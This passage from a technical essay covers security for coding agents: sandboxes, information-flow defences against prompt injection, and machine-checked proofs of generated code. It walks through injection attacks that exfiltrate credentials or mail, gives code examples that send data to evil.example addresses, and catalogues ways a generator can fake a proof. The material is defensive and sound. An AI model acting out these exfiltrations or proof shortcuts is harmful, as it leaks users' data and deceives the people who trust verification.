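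The testers were not working on their own projects, so they may have cared less than usual about the consequences. Anthropic was also making the case for its own automated check, which blocked 89% of the same commands. Even so, the decline over a session fits approval fatigue, and *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) likewise warns that repeated approvals may reflect tiredness or pressure to deliver rather than trust. Users do seem to read some requests. They reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, compared with 3% of permission requests, perhaps because plans come up less often and are easier to judge.

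Reviewing commands attentively wouldn't be enough, because a command often doesn't reveal its effects. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that user review played a part in 105. In 80 of these, the user had let the agent act without asking, and in 31 the prompt didn't show what the command would do (some reports fell into both groups). For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine but runs whatever the script contains. The command to install the malicious PDF package would look just as ordinary, and a careful developer might well approve it. A sandbox restricts what the package can do, however harmless the command looks.

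Approval also fails when somebody has deceived the user. In an exercise at Anthropic, a researcher posing as a helpful colleague emailed an employee a prompt to run in Claude Code. The prompt mixed ordinary steps with an instruction to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 runs. The instruction came from the employee, so the model had little basis for flagging it. File rules that hid the credentials or network rules that blocked the address would have stopped the leak.

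But a sandbox works only if somebody sets it up correctly, and *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) makes this a condition for running commands without approval. A sandbox also takes upkeep. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* acknowledges that each new capability needs configuring. *SideKernel* reports, anecdotally, that most users of coding agents seem to run no sandbox at all, and this extra work may be why. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission prompts. If a developer has neither prompts nor a sandbox, a malicious package gets everything described at the start of this section.

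The two methods work best together. The sandbox can handle routine commands, which leaves the user with a few decisions that deserve attention, such as whether to allow a new network address. Neither method replaces rules about how an agent may use its permitted tools, such as a database it can write to.

### What leaves the sandbox

A sandbox limits side effects but doesn't check whether the code is correct. The bill-splitting function still loses its penny when it runs in a microVM. Once merged, code runs outside the sandbox with the finished product's permissions. A malicious package could behave perfectly during the tests and start copying customer data once it detects real orders, so a sandbox run with no suspicious activity is poor evidence that a dependency is safe. Production systems therefore need their own limits on files, network access and credentials.

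Files written in the sandbox are untrusted input to any program on the host that reads them. This matters most when the sandbox shares the developer's working folder, because ordinary development tools run some of those files automatically:

- Git hooks, which are scripts that Git runs on actions such as a commit,
- build files, which run when somebody builds or installs the project,
- editor settings, which can start tasks when somebody opens the folder,
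- settings for coding agents, which can contain start-up commands.

If the malicious package changes one of these, its code runs on the host the next time the developer commits or opens the project. Docker advises reviewing the files before using them, as one would a pull request from an untrusted contributor. The usual review can miss Git hooks because they don't appear in `git diff`. Clone mode avoids that problem, since Git doesn't transfer hooks when the host fetches the agent's commits, but the fetched commits can still contain altered build files and settings.

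Test reports and logs need the same checks as a model's replies. If another agent reads a log, a line in it can act as a prompt injection. A program that unpacks an archive from the sandbox also has to check where each file will land. The host can avoid many of these problems by accepting only the commits and a small record in a fixed format, such as the number of tests that passed and failed, and checking that record as `read_label` checks a label. Docker also warns that a local sandbox can write to the host's clipboard, so a developer should check the clipboard's contents before pasting them into a terminal.

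Pushing the agent's branch can start an automated build on another server, where the package runs again, possibly with access to the passwords for deploying the shop. That build needs a sandbox too, and it shouldn't receive those passwords until a person has reviewed the change.

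## Checking an agent's actions against permissions and data-flow rules

A sandbox that lets an agent send email does not stop it from sending the wrong file to the wrong person. In *Guardians of the Agents*, the computer scientist Erik Meijer describes an assistant with two tools, one for fetching mail and one for sending it. A user asks it to summarize her inbox. One message there says that, for legal compliance, the assistant must send a summary to an outside address and not mention doing so. The assistant obeys, then shows the user a summary that omits that message.

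Both tool calls look ordinary, but the second is harmful because its recipient came from a stranger's email and its content came from a private inbox. A list of permitted tools doesn't cover where the data came from. One remedy is to treat the agent's plan as an untrusted program and check each step before it runs, including the source of its data.

### How CaMeL separates the plan from the data

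Google DeepMind's CaMeL, published in 2025, builds on Willison's earlier idea of dividing an agent between two models. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

1. A planner model reads the user's request but none of the data that the tools will return. It writes a plan in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan and makes the tool calls.
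3. When the plan needs something from an untrusted text, the interpreter gives the text to a second model, which has no tools. The interpreter stores this reader model's answer in a variable, and the planner never sees it.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources (where it came from) and its readers (who may see it). A value computed from others inherits their restrictions.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy. This is a short Python function that examines the tool, its arguments and their labels, then allows or denies the call.

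A prompt injection in an email can therefore change a value but can't add a step to the plan. The policies are needed because a changed value alone can do harm.

### Example: a planted address

Suppose Ann tells her agent, "Send Bob the document named in the notes. His address is in there too." The planner writes this:

```
notes = read_file("notes.txt")
name = ask_reader("Which document should Bob get?", notes)
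address = ask_reader("What is Bob's address?", notes)
doc = read_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=doc)
```

Ann, Bob and Carol can all read the notes. An attacker has managed to replace Bob's address in them with `bob@evil.example`. When the plan reaches its last line, the variables look like this:

| Variable | Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | Text of the notes | Notes (untrusted) | Ann, Bob, Carol |
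| `name` | `budget.xlsx` | Notes (untrusted) | Ann, Bob, Carol |
| `address` | `bob@evil.example` | Notes (untrusted) | Ann, Bob, Carol |
| `doc` | Contents of the budget | File store, and the notes that named the file | Ann, Bob |

The policy for `send_email` checks the recipient against the attachment's list of permitted readers. That list includes Ann's and Bob's real addresses but not `bob@evil.example`, so the interpreter refuses the call.

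If the notes contained Bob's real address, the same call would go through. A stricter policy could require the address itself to come from a trusted source. Nikolaou and colleagues use that rule in a similar example, where it blocks the plan no matter which address the messages contain. The planner can satisfy the rule by looking Bob up in Ann's contacts.

The attacker could instead change the document's name in the notes. If the new name refers to a salary file that only Ann may read, the readers check stops the call. But if it refers to a different file that Bob may read, Bob gets the wrong document.

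The general rule is that data may flow only to recipients its label allows. Let *R*(*x*) be the set of people who may read *x*. A value made from *x* and *y* can be read only by the people in both sets, *R*(*x*) ∩ *R*(*y*), and a call may send *z* to a group *G* only if *G* ⊆ *R*(*z*). In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) add a rule about trust. A value is trusted only if everything that influenced it is trusted, and a consequential action, such as a payment, must depend only on trusted values. They point out that the data-flow rule alone limits what an action can leak but doesn't stop an injection from triggering the action.

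### What the protection costs

AgentDojo is a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated settings (office work, travel, banking and the chat program Slack), plus attacks hidden in the data that tools return. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent.

Later reruns with the policies enforced found a much larger drop in completed tasks. In *Kairos* (2026), CaMeL cut the attack success rate from 28.3% to 0.4%, but the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 87.0% to 40.4%. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks on CaMeL succeeded, but it completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks. Both papers present rival defences, and the results also depend on the choice of model.

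Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with the small model Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks. It completed 49 of the 97 tasks and blocked 26. In the other 22, the plan passed the checks but didn't do what the user wanted.

CaMeL also uses more computing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that, for the median AgentDojo task, it used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an agent with no defence.

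Stronger models seem to cope better with planning in advance. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL without any policies on tasks that several agents share. The completion rate fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5.

The benefit is also harder to measure on strong models. Without any defence, GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks in Peters-Gill and colleagues' multi-agent version of AgentDojo. They caution that this result may reflect the benchmark's attacks, since attacks that adapt to the model have succeeded against every frontier model tried in large tests.

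### FIDES and its successors

Microsoft's FIDES, which Costa and colleagues designed, lets the model choose each step after seeing the result of the last, as an ordinary agent does. When a tool returns data less trusted than the conversation so far, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or have a second model, which has no tools, answer a question about its contents.

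FIDES can restrict that answer to a type. For example, when a user asks the agent to check three emails and create a calendar entry if one contains a meeting request, the second model can answer only yes or no. A policy can let that answer determine the next step because an attacker can make the answer wrong but can't use it to pass on instructions, as in the workflow with three labels.

The table shows the share of AgentDojo tasks each agent completed with GPT-4o when there were no attacks. The last row gives the share of tasks in which the right steps depend on what the agent reads.

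| | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |
| Tasks that depend on the data | 5.0% | 10.0% | 43.8% | 42.9% |

In AgentDojo, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent, which has no checks. Three attacks were scored as successful against FIDES, which does have them, but Costa and colleagues inspected the three and found no real violation. Hiding data in variables lets FIDES complete many tasks that the checks would otherwise block, though it still completes only about half as many banking and Slack tasks as an unprotected agent.

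Among the 2026 successors, the strongest guarantee comes from Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*. They designed a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label, and proved in Lean that the labels control what data can influence. One motivation was a gap in CaMeL's tracking. In this example, adapted from theirs, the account balance is secret:

```
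rich = True
poor = True
if balance > 1000000: poor = False
if poor: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `poor` to false and marks it as secret. The program skips the assignment on the fourth line, so `rich` keeps its original public label and the email goes out. No email goes out if the balance is low, so the recipient can learn something about the balance even though the message contains no secret value.

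Garby and colleagues tested an agent written in their language, called Randori, on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models. Attacks succeeded in only 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and roughly twice as many as CaMeL did with policies, which completed the task in 18 of 48 runs.

Randori keeps these tasks possible by letting the planner mark a piece of untrusted data as trusted before the agent reads any of it. Both successful attacks exploited such an exception. The user had asked the agent to make a payment by following the instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without exceptions, Randori blocks this attack but also fails some legitimate tasks.

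Of the experiment's 144 combinations of task and attack, 97 required a tool call or file read that the plan would never contain. Planning first generally stops these attacks even without labels, so the policies matter mainly for the other 47.

In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) report that the share of tasks completed fell by at most three percentage points. However, the version they tested can restore calls that one of its checks has blocked, while the full proof covers a stricter version.

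*Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) helps an agent recover after a blocked call. In one example, an agent that has to reorder a shirt looks for a checkout code in the user's email, reads a planted message and tries to buy another product. A check finds that the product number came from the email, blocks the purchase and tells the agent to use the order history. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of more changeable tasks, no attacks succeeded and the agent completed more tasks than it did without a defence. However, many of the policies were specific to one task, such as requiring the shirt to come from the order history. A business would need rules that work for requests it hasn't seen.

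### When one agent instructs another

Protecting each agent separately doesn't protect the group. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which one CaMeL agent reads a database of job applicants, a second coordinates the work and a third sends messages. The user asks the system to send Julie a summary on Slack, but the database contains a hidden instruction to email the data to an outside address.

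The first two agents treat the database text as untrusted data. But the coordinator pastes its summary into the request it sends to the third agent, whose planner treats the whole request as trusted. The planner then adds a step that emails the data to the attacker.

The fix resembles a parameterised query. The coordinator sends a fixed instruction and puts the summary in a separate variable, which the third agent's planner can't read. Across five models, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and zero with the separate variable.

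### Proving a plan before it runs

CaMeL checks each tool call when the plan reaches it, and by then earlier steps may have had effects that are hard to undo. Meijer proposes checking the whole plan first. The model writes a structured workflow, a verifier tests it against the rules, and no tool runs until the workflow passes. In the inbox example, a rule could forbid any data flow from fetched mail to the body of a message addressed outside the company.

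Meijer (2026), in *Return of the Theorem*, suggests writing business rules as Horn clauses, which state that a conclusion follows if all the listed conditions hold. An automatic solver then checks the plan against them. For example, a shop might have two rules for refunds:

```
may_refund(order) if total(order) <= 200
may_refund(order) if approved(order)
```

Suppose the agent's plan looks up an order and refunds it. The solver tries to prove that `may_refund` holds for every order that could reach the refund step. It finds a counterexample, an unapproved order for 300, so the verifier rejects the plan. The agent can add a step that requests approval for totals above 200 and stops if it is denied. The solver can then prove that the plan obeys the rules for every order, provided the tools report totals and approvals correctly.

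A rule has to cover unwanted effects as well as the intended result. In another of Meijer's examples, a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the agent plans to delete every text file with `*.txt`. This plan satisfies a rule that requires only that the two files be gone. The verifier rejects it if the rule also requires all other files to remain unchanged.

CaMeLoT adds a check of this kind to CaMeL. It converts the plan into a diagram of possible steps, and a program called a model checker searches the diagram for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, the planner gets the path as feedback and can repair the plan. Nikolaou and colleagues could check 22 of 28 CaMeL policies before the plan runs. The other six depend on facts known only during the run, such as who can currently read a shared file, so CaMeL still has to check those policies then.

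Checking the whole plan also allows rules about what must happen later. For example, a rule can require that every security incident the agent opens is eventually resolved or passed to a specialist. CaMeL's policies can't naturally express such rules because they run one call at a time.

### Permission rules in Cedar

Cedar is a language for access rules from Amazon's cloud company AWS. In simplified form, a Cedar rule for small refunds could look like this:

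```
permit(principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when { context.input.amount <= 200 };
```

In AWS's system for agents, a gateway between the agent and its tools blocks every call unless a rule permits it. AWS argues that this gives a company a single checkpoint outside the agent, which the model can't bypass. This is true only for tools the agent reaches through the gateway.

Cedar is easier to adopt than Meijer's proposal because the agent doesn't have to write a plan. The gateway evaluates each call's actual arguments, so it doesn't need a proof that covers every possible order. But it may stop an agent halfway through a job, for example after cancelling an order but before refunding the customer. The rule above would also allow ten refunds of 200 in a row, and it doesn't check whether the order number came from the customer or from a planted message. Dogwood, an extension of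 Cedar, adds rules that depend on the agent's earlier actions, according to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026).

A company could reasonably start with Cedar rules for spending limits and forbidden tools, then add data-flow labels where an agent handles both private data and text from strangers. Proving plans in advance seems most useful for work with settled procedures and steps that are hard to reverse.

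### Where the rules run out

Somebody has to write the policies and label the data. Costa and colleagues labelled a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it, but a company doesn't know in advance which fields an attacker will use. Costa and colleagues also inferred an email's readers from its sender and recipients, although somebody may have shared it more widely. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) describes a tool that saves work by converting rules in ordinary English to Cedar, but a person should still read the result, since a mistranslated rule could permit the wrong calls.

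Some tasks need untrusted text to steer the plan. An agent can't work through a to-do list without reading it, so anyone who can edit the list can give the agent work. In *AgentDyn* (2026), GPT-4o agents completed far fewer tasks with any of the tested defences than without one. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) lets the agent read such text in a temporary branch that can return only an answer in a fixed format. That answer may still be false, so the agent should probably ask the user before making a large payment.

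A permitted action can also be a mistake. Text in an email can cause the reader model to return an empty summary, which the agent then sends to the right person. The planner can misinterpret a benign request. If Ann's agent mistakenly sends Bob last year's budget, the checks still pass because the labels are correct and Bob is allowed to read it.

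## How a generated program is proved correct

Deductive verification proves, by reasoning about a program's text, that the program meets its specification on every permitted input. It can catch errors that other techniques miss. For example, an agent that obeys every permission rule may still add up an invoice wrongly, and tests may not catch the mistake.

For decades few projects used deductive verification, because experts had to write the proofs by hand. Language models can now write many of these proofs, and proof checkers work the same way whether a person or a model wrote the proof.

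### Contracts and loop invariants

A function's specification usually takes the form of a contract. The precondition states what must be true when the function starts, and the postcondition states what must be true when it returns. In Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, the keywords are `requires` and `ensures`. Breen, Letson and colleagues (2026), in *AxDafny*, use an example like this one, which adds the whole numbers from 0 to *n*:

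```
method Sum(n: int) returns (s: int)
  requires 0 <= n
  ensures s == n * (n + 1) / 2
{
  s := 0;
  var i := 0;
  while i < n
    invariant s == i * (i + 1) / 2
    invariant 0 <= i <= n
  {
    i := i + 1;
    s := s + i;
  }
}
```

The loop makes this hard to verify because it can run any number of times, and the verifier can't examine each case separately. The solution is a loop invariant, a statement that is true before the loop starts and after every pass. Here the invariants are that `i` is between 0 and `n`, and that `s` is the sum of the numbers up to `i`.

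The contract is part of the specification, so whoever wants the program should control it. The generator is free to choose the invariants, because they are part of the proof and have no effect when the program runs.

### Three obligations

The verifier never runs the loop. It converts the method into logical formulas, called verification conditions or proof obligations. If all of them hold, the method meets its contract. The loop in `Sum` produces three:

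| Obligation | What the verifier may assume | What it must show |
|---|---|---|
| Start | *n* ≥ 0, *i* = 0, *s* = 0 | 0 ≤ *i* ≤ *n* and *s* = *i*(*i* + 1)/2 |
| Step | 0 ≤ *i* ≤ *n*, *s* = *i*(*i* + 1)/2, *i* < *n* | 0 ≤ *i* + 1 ≤ *n* and *s* + (*i* + 1) = (*i* + 1)(*i* + 2)/2 |
| Exit | 0 ≤ *i* ≤ *n*, *s* = *i*(*i* + 1)/2, *i* ≥ *n* | *s* = *n*(*n* + 1)/2 |

**Start.** Both invariants hold before the first pass, since 0 lies between 0 and *n* and 0 = 0 × 1/2.

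**Step.** The verifier gets this formula by working backwards through the loop body. The invariant *s* = *i*(*i* + 1)/2 has to hold after the pass. The last line of the body adds `i` to `s`, so the verifier replaces *s* with *s* + *i*. The line before it adds 1 to `i`, so the verifier then replaces every *i* with *i* + 1. The result is the equation in the table. It holds because

*i*(*i* + 1)/2 + (*i* + 1) = (*i*(*i* + 1) + 2(*i* + 1))/2 = (*i* + 1)(*i* + 2)/2

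The other invariant also survives the pass, because a whole number below *n* is still at most *n* after adding 1.

The loop exits only when *i* ≥ *n*, and the invariant gives *i* ≤ *n*, so *i* = *n*. Substituting *n* for *i* in the invariant about *s* gives the postcondition.

The verifier also has to show that the loop ends. The loop must end because *n* − *i* falls by one on each pass and can't go below zero.

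Suppose a generator makes the loop stop one step early by writing `while i < n - 1`. The start obligation doesn't change. The step obligation still holds, because the new condition gives the verifier a stronger assumption. The exit obligation fails because the verifier can now assume only *i* ≥ *n* − 1, so *i* may equal *n* − 1, which makes *s* too small by *n*. The smallest counterexample is *n* = 1, *i* = 0 and *s* = 0, where the method returns 0 and the contract requires 1. Dafny rejects the method and reports that it can't prove the postcondition. A unit test that tried only *n* = 0 would pass.

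The exit obligation also fails if the generator writes the loop correctly but leaves out the invariant about `s`, because the verifier then has no information about `s` after the loop. A rejection therefore doesn't prove the program is wrong. *Diversifying to Verify* (Yu and Martins, 2026) notes that the cause may also be a weak invariant, a missing argument that the loop ends, or a fact the solver needed but didn't have.

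### Automatic solvers and proof checkers

*From Natural Language to Verified Code* (Erfan, Chowdhury et al., 2026) explains that Dafny translates a program into an intermediate language called Boogie and passes the resulting formulas to the solver Z3. For each proof obligation, Z3 looks for values that make the assumptions true and the conclusion false. If it shows that none exist, the obligation holds. If it finds some, they are a possible counterexample. It may also time out without an answer.

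Verus does the same for programs in Rust. It must also prove that arithmetic doesn't overflow, because Rust's ordinary integers have a fixed size, while Dafny's `int` has no upper limit. If `s` were an unsigned 32-bit integer, the sum would overflow for any *n* above 92,681, and Verus would reject the method unless a precondition excluded those values.

In Lean and Rocq, by contrast, somebody has to supply the proof, usually as a list of commands called tactics. To prove the formula for the sum, the tactics would show that it holds for 0, and that if it holds for some number *k* it also holds for *k* + 1. The system builds a fully detailed proof from these commands, and a small program called the kernel accepts it only if every step follows from fixed logical rules. In Rocq the command `Qed` triggers this check, according to *A Case Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs in Verification* (2025).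 The tactics can come from a careless or hostile author, because the kernel checks the proof they produce.

Solvers save work on arithmetic and other routine reasoning. Proof checkers can handle much more general mathematics, and they depend on less code being correct. Both leave open who writes the parts of a proof that a machine can't find alone.

### Why the author needs no trust

In 1996, Necula and Lee, in *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, proposed a way for an operating system to run machine code from strangers. Necula, in *Proof-Carrying Code*, set out the general method the following year. The party that wants to run the code, called the consumer, publishes a safety policy, such as which parts of memory a program may read. The rest takes four steps:

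1. The producer writes the program and its loop invariants.
2. The producer works out the verification condition, proves it, and sends the proof along with the code.
3. The consumer works out the verification condition again from the code it received.
4. The consumer checks that the proof proves exactly this formula, then runs the code as often as it likes.

The third step protects the consumer. If somebody alters the code in transit, the formula usually changes, the proof no longer matches it and the consumer rejects the program. If the proof is still valid, the altered program also obeys the policy. A false invariant does no harm either, because the resulting formula cannot be proved. A digital signature is weaker protection because it shows only who produced the code, and Necula notes that even trusted people make mistakes or act maliciously.

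The method also moves the hard work to the producer, who may need long searches or human help to find a proof. Checking the proof is quick and mechanical. Necula tested the method on packet filters, which are small programs that run inside the operating system and select network traffic for an application. His filters were hand-written in machine code, needed no safety checks while running, and were ten times as fast as equivalent filters run through a standard interpreter.

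With generated code, the language model is the producer and the team that wants the program is the consumer. The team keeps the specification and runs the checker itself.

If the checker is sound and the specification is right, the false acceptance rate is zero. The formula for retrying against an imperfect test then shows that 100% of accepted programs are correct, whatever the model's success rate. Retries can waste computing time, but they can't cause a wrong program to be accepted. Both conditions can fail in practice, since checkers have bugs and postconditions can be too weak.

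### Why no checker can decide every program

No tool can take any program and any contract and, without invariants or proofs, always correctly determine whether the program meets the contract. This follows from Rice's theorem, published in 1953. The theorem covers any property of what a program computes, rather than of its text, that some programs have and others lack. No algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has such a property.

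No tool can always tell whether a method meets the contract of `Sum`. For any program *A*, one can write a method that runs *A*, discards the result, and then computes the sum correctly. This method meets the contract exactly when *A* eventually stops, because otherwise it never returns a sum. A tool that could always tell whether a method meets the contract could therefore determine whether any program stops, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that.

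A tool that never accepts a wrong program must therefore fail to accept some correct ones. A proof checker avoids this problem because it only has to check whether a given text of finite length is a valid proof. Turing and Alonzo Church also showed that no procedure can decide whether an arbitrary mathematical statement has a proof, as *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) recounts. Finding proofs therefore requires either people or something that guesses well, and a language model can do the guessing without anyone having to trust it.

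Verifiers also reject many programs that may well be correct, for reasons that have little to do with these theoretical limits. Yu and Martins had a model solve each of 73 programming tasks in four styles, using either arrays or lists and either loops or recursion. They ran all 292 programs through Why3, a verifier that also relies on automatic solvers. It accepted 32.9% at first and 52.7% after two rounds of repairs to the annotations. It accepted at least one version for 49 of the tasks, compared with 44 for the best single style. Writing a program in a different style can therefore make it provable, but the gain here was modest.

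### Generate, check and repair

Systems that generate verified code nearly all use the same loop. The model writes a program, the missing annotations, or both. The verifier checks the result, and any error messages go back to the model for another attempt. The loop ends when the verifier accepts the result or the attempts run out. In 2025, Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It* described Anthropic's Claude Code doing this in Lean and often reaching a correct proof after several rounds. The article said the work had still probably taken longer than it would have by hand, because of rare conceptual mistakes that caused no error message.

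Letting a model repair its failed attempts makes a large difference. On DafnyBench, a set of 782 Dafny programs with the invariants and other hints removed, Gemini 3.1 Pro restored enough hints to verify 68.5% of the programs in a single attempt. With up to 20 attempts inside AxDafny, Breen and colleagues' system, it reached 92.7%. AxDafny gives the model its full previous attempt, the verifier's messages about it, and notes on lessons from earlier attempts. Most of the gain came in the first five rounds.

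Some failed proofs can be repaired without a model. *DafnyPro* (Banerjee, Bouissou and Zetzsche, 2026) found that models often add invariants that the proof doesn't need and the verifier can't establish, and that one such invariant makes the whole attempt fail. DafnyPro deletes these invariants and runs the verifier again before going back to the model. It also gives the model eight general hints. One is to state in the program that a slice containing every element of an array is equal to the whole array, because the solver, Z3, may not use that fact otherwise. On DafnyBench with Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the hints added about 10 percentage points to the success rate and the deletions about 3.

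Testing an invariant before trying to prove it also helps. Wesselink, Huizing and van de Wetering (2026), in *LLM-Assisted Verification in Dafny*, run a Python copy of the program on random inputs and discard any invariant that turns out false. They then look for invariants that are true but too weak. In `Sum`, for example, `s` is never 2, because the totals run 0, 1, 3, 6 and so on. But "`s` is not 2" can't serve as an invariant on its own, because it permits the state `i` = 0 and `s` = 1, from which one pass of the loop gives `s` = 2. The tool finds such cases by altering states from real runs and executing one more pass.

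How well a repair loop works is limited by the quality of its error messages. A failed tactic in Rocq leaves a precise statement of what remains to be proved. A solver that runs out of time may give no reason, so it is unclear whether the claim was false, a fact was missing, or the formula was too large. Wesselink and colleagues used their invariant tester on seven failures that had persisted through every attempt to make the proof easier for the solver, and the statement was false in all seven.

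### How a generator can fake a proof

The easiest way to make `Sum` pass verification is to add one line at the end:

`assume s == n * (n + 1) / 2;`

Dafny accepts an assumption as true without proof, so the postcondition follows even if the loop is wrong or missing. Programmers use assumptions to postpone part of a proof, but a generator rewarded for passing the verifier may leave them in. *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* (2026) gives an example in which a model was supposed to prove correct a function that checks whether every number in a list is below a threshold. The model copied the postcondition into an `assume` statement. *TLA-Verus* (2026) points out that Verus still reports no errors when a proof takes such a shortcut.

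| Shortcut | Example | Check that blocks it |
|---|---|---|
| Assume the conclusion | `assume` in Dafny and Verus, `sorry` in Lean, `Admitted` in Rocq | Reject these constructs in anything the generator writes |
| Add an axiom | A false lemma that Verus accepts because of the label `axiom` | List the axioms behind each proof and accept only standard ones |
| Switch off verification | `{:verify false}` in Dafny, `external_body` in Verus | Reject these labels |
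| Weaken the contract | Replace a postcondition with `ensures true` | Compare the contract with the original, or restore it |
| Edit the program | Change a starting value so that the proof becomes easier | Remove all annotations and compare the rest with the original |
| Change a definition | Redefine `<=` so that every comparison is true | Lock every definition that the contract uses |

DafnyPro focuses on edits to the program. In one case, a model that had to add invariants to a sorting routine changed the opening line from `b := a+1` to `b := a`, and the verifier then accepted a different program from the one it was supposed to check. DafnyPro uses Dafny's own parser to strip the annotations from the model's version, and rejects the attempt unless the remaining code is identical to the original. Because this comparison ignores annotations, it misses any assumptions hidden among them, and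 those need a second check.

AxDafny checks whether a model has changed the specification or bypassed the proof. It requires every original `requires` and `ensures` clause to reappear in the model's file, and it rejects any file containing `assume`, `{:axiom}`, `{:verify false}` or `{:extern}`, which marks code that Dafny accepts without checking. After the verifier has run, a second model checks for tricks that these rules miss, such as rewriting a definition so that it is always true.

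The rule about original clauses also has a gap, since it allows new clauses to be added. A generator could keep the contract of `Sum` and add `requires n == 0`, which makes the task trivial. The reviewing model might catch this, but an exact comparison of the main method's contract certainly would. Wesselink and colleagues use a stricter lock that covers the contract and every definition it depends on, including those in libraries. Only a person can approve a change.

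Searching the text for forbidden words is unreliable. One of the tricks listed in *TLA-Verus* imports the command `admit`, which accepts a goal without proof, under the name `shh`, so a search for calls to `admit` would find none. Lean and Rocq offer a more reliable method, because each can list every assumption a finished proof relies on. *Vero* (2026), a test of whether agents can build verified software in Lean, accepts only Lean's three standard axioms. *LLVM Translation Validation Automated with Large Language Models and Lean* (2026) applies the same rule to proofs that a compiler has preserved a program's meaning. For Rocq, *Growing an Agent/Prover Interface* (2026) also describes recompiling the file in a clean folder and forbidding new imports, because they could hide altered definitions.

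In one of *Vero*'s test runs, an agent proved 25 of 53 specifications, and these checks rejected its proofs of the other 28 because they relied on shortcuts. *Vero* also guards against a subtler trick that exploits a Lean feature, which lets a programmer attach a fast function to run in place of the one the proof describes. An agent could copy the specification's own definition, prove the copy correct, and attach unrelated, unproved code.

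A false acceptance rate of zero therefore depends on the whole acceptance procedure, not just the verifier. As with hidden tests, the team should run all of it where the generator can't change anything.

### Results on benchmarks

In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) gave nine models a specification for each task and asked for a program and its proof, allowing five attempts on most tasks. The best single model solved 67.5% of the tasks in Dafny (Claude Opus 4.1), 30.9% in Verus (GPT-5) and 17.9% in Lean (GPT-5). The more widely quoted figures of 82%, 44% and 27% count a task as solved if any of the nine models solved it. All of these models are now more than a year old.

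DafnyBench is an easier test, because the program and its contract are given and the model adds only the hints.

| Published | Source | Model | Verified on DafnyBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| September 2025 | Bursuc and colleagues | Claude Opus 4.1 | 89.2% |
| January 2026 | Banerjee and colleagues | Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 86.2% |
| June 2026 | Breen and colleagues | GPT-5.5, medium effort | 88.9% |
| June 2026 | Breen and colleagues | Gemini 3.1 Pro | 92.7% |

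DafnyPro's 86% is in one respect the most impressive of these scores, because a much older model achieved it, with ten attempts per program. The scores aren't strictly comparable, though. Banerjee and colleagues argue that cheating inflated some earlier ones, since the benchmark's original checks missed certain edits. They also repaired 70 programs that didn't compile, which raised their own score by 3.6 percentage points. With scores around 90%, DafnyBench no longer distinguishes good systems from very good ones.

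Writing both the program and the proof is harder than writing the proof alone. Breen and colleagues translated 250 competition problems into Dafny specifications. AxDafny solved 56.4% of them, including 28% of the hardest group, while GPT-5.5 solved 11.6% in a single attempt.

They then compiled the verified solutions to the easy and medium problems into Python and ran the competition's tests. Of 127 verified programs, 38 passed, 83 were too slow and 6 used too much memory. None gave a wrong answer, as one would hope after a proof, but the contracts set no limit on time or memory, and a slow, simple program is often easier to prove correct. Dafny's translation into Python also caused part of the slowness.

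Small open models can also write verified programs, although the evidence is limited. Erfan and colleagues tested seven of them on 11 problems, and nearly all failed when given only a description. When given the method's signature and feedback from the verifier, Gemma 4 31B produced verified programs for 10 of the 11. The models wrote their own contracts, which could have been trivial, so the researchers also ran the programs on public test data.

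### Two larger projects

In *Trustworthy Software Project Generation*, Fang and Xiong (2026) had an agent based on Claude Opus 4.7 build an interpreter that lets other machines run code for RISC-V processors. It supports the 47 instructions of the basic 32-bit set. The agent worked from the processor manual and finished in 30 minutes, with no human help after the start. It wrote 1,859 lines of Rocq, about half of them specifications and proofs, and a tool converted the verified functions into 2,848 lines of C++.

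The JALR instruction jumps to an address held in a register and saves the return address. The agent proved that JALR saves the right return address, jumps to the right place, and always sets the last bit of the new address to zero. It also proved that JALR leaves memory and all other registers unchanged. Without that last property, an implementation could jump correctly but damage an unrelated register.

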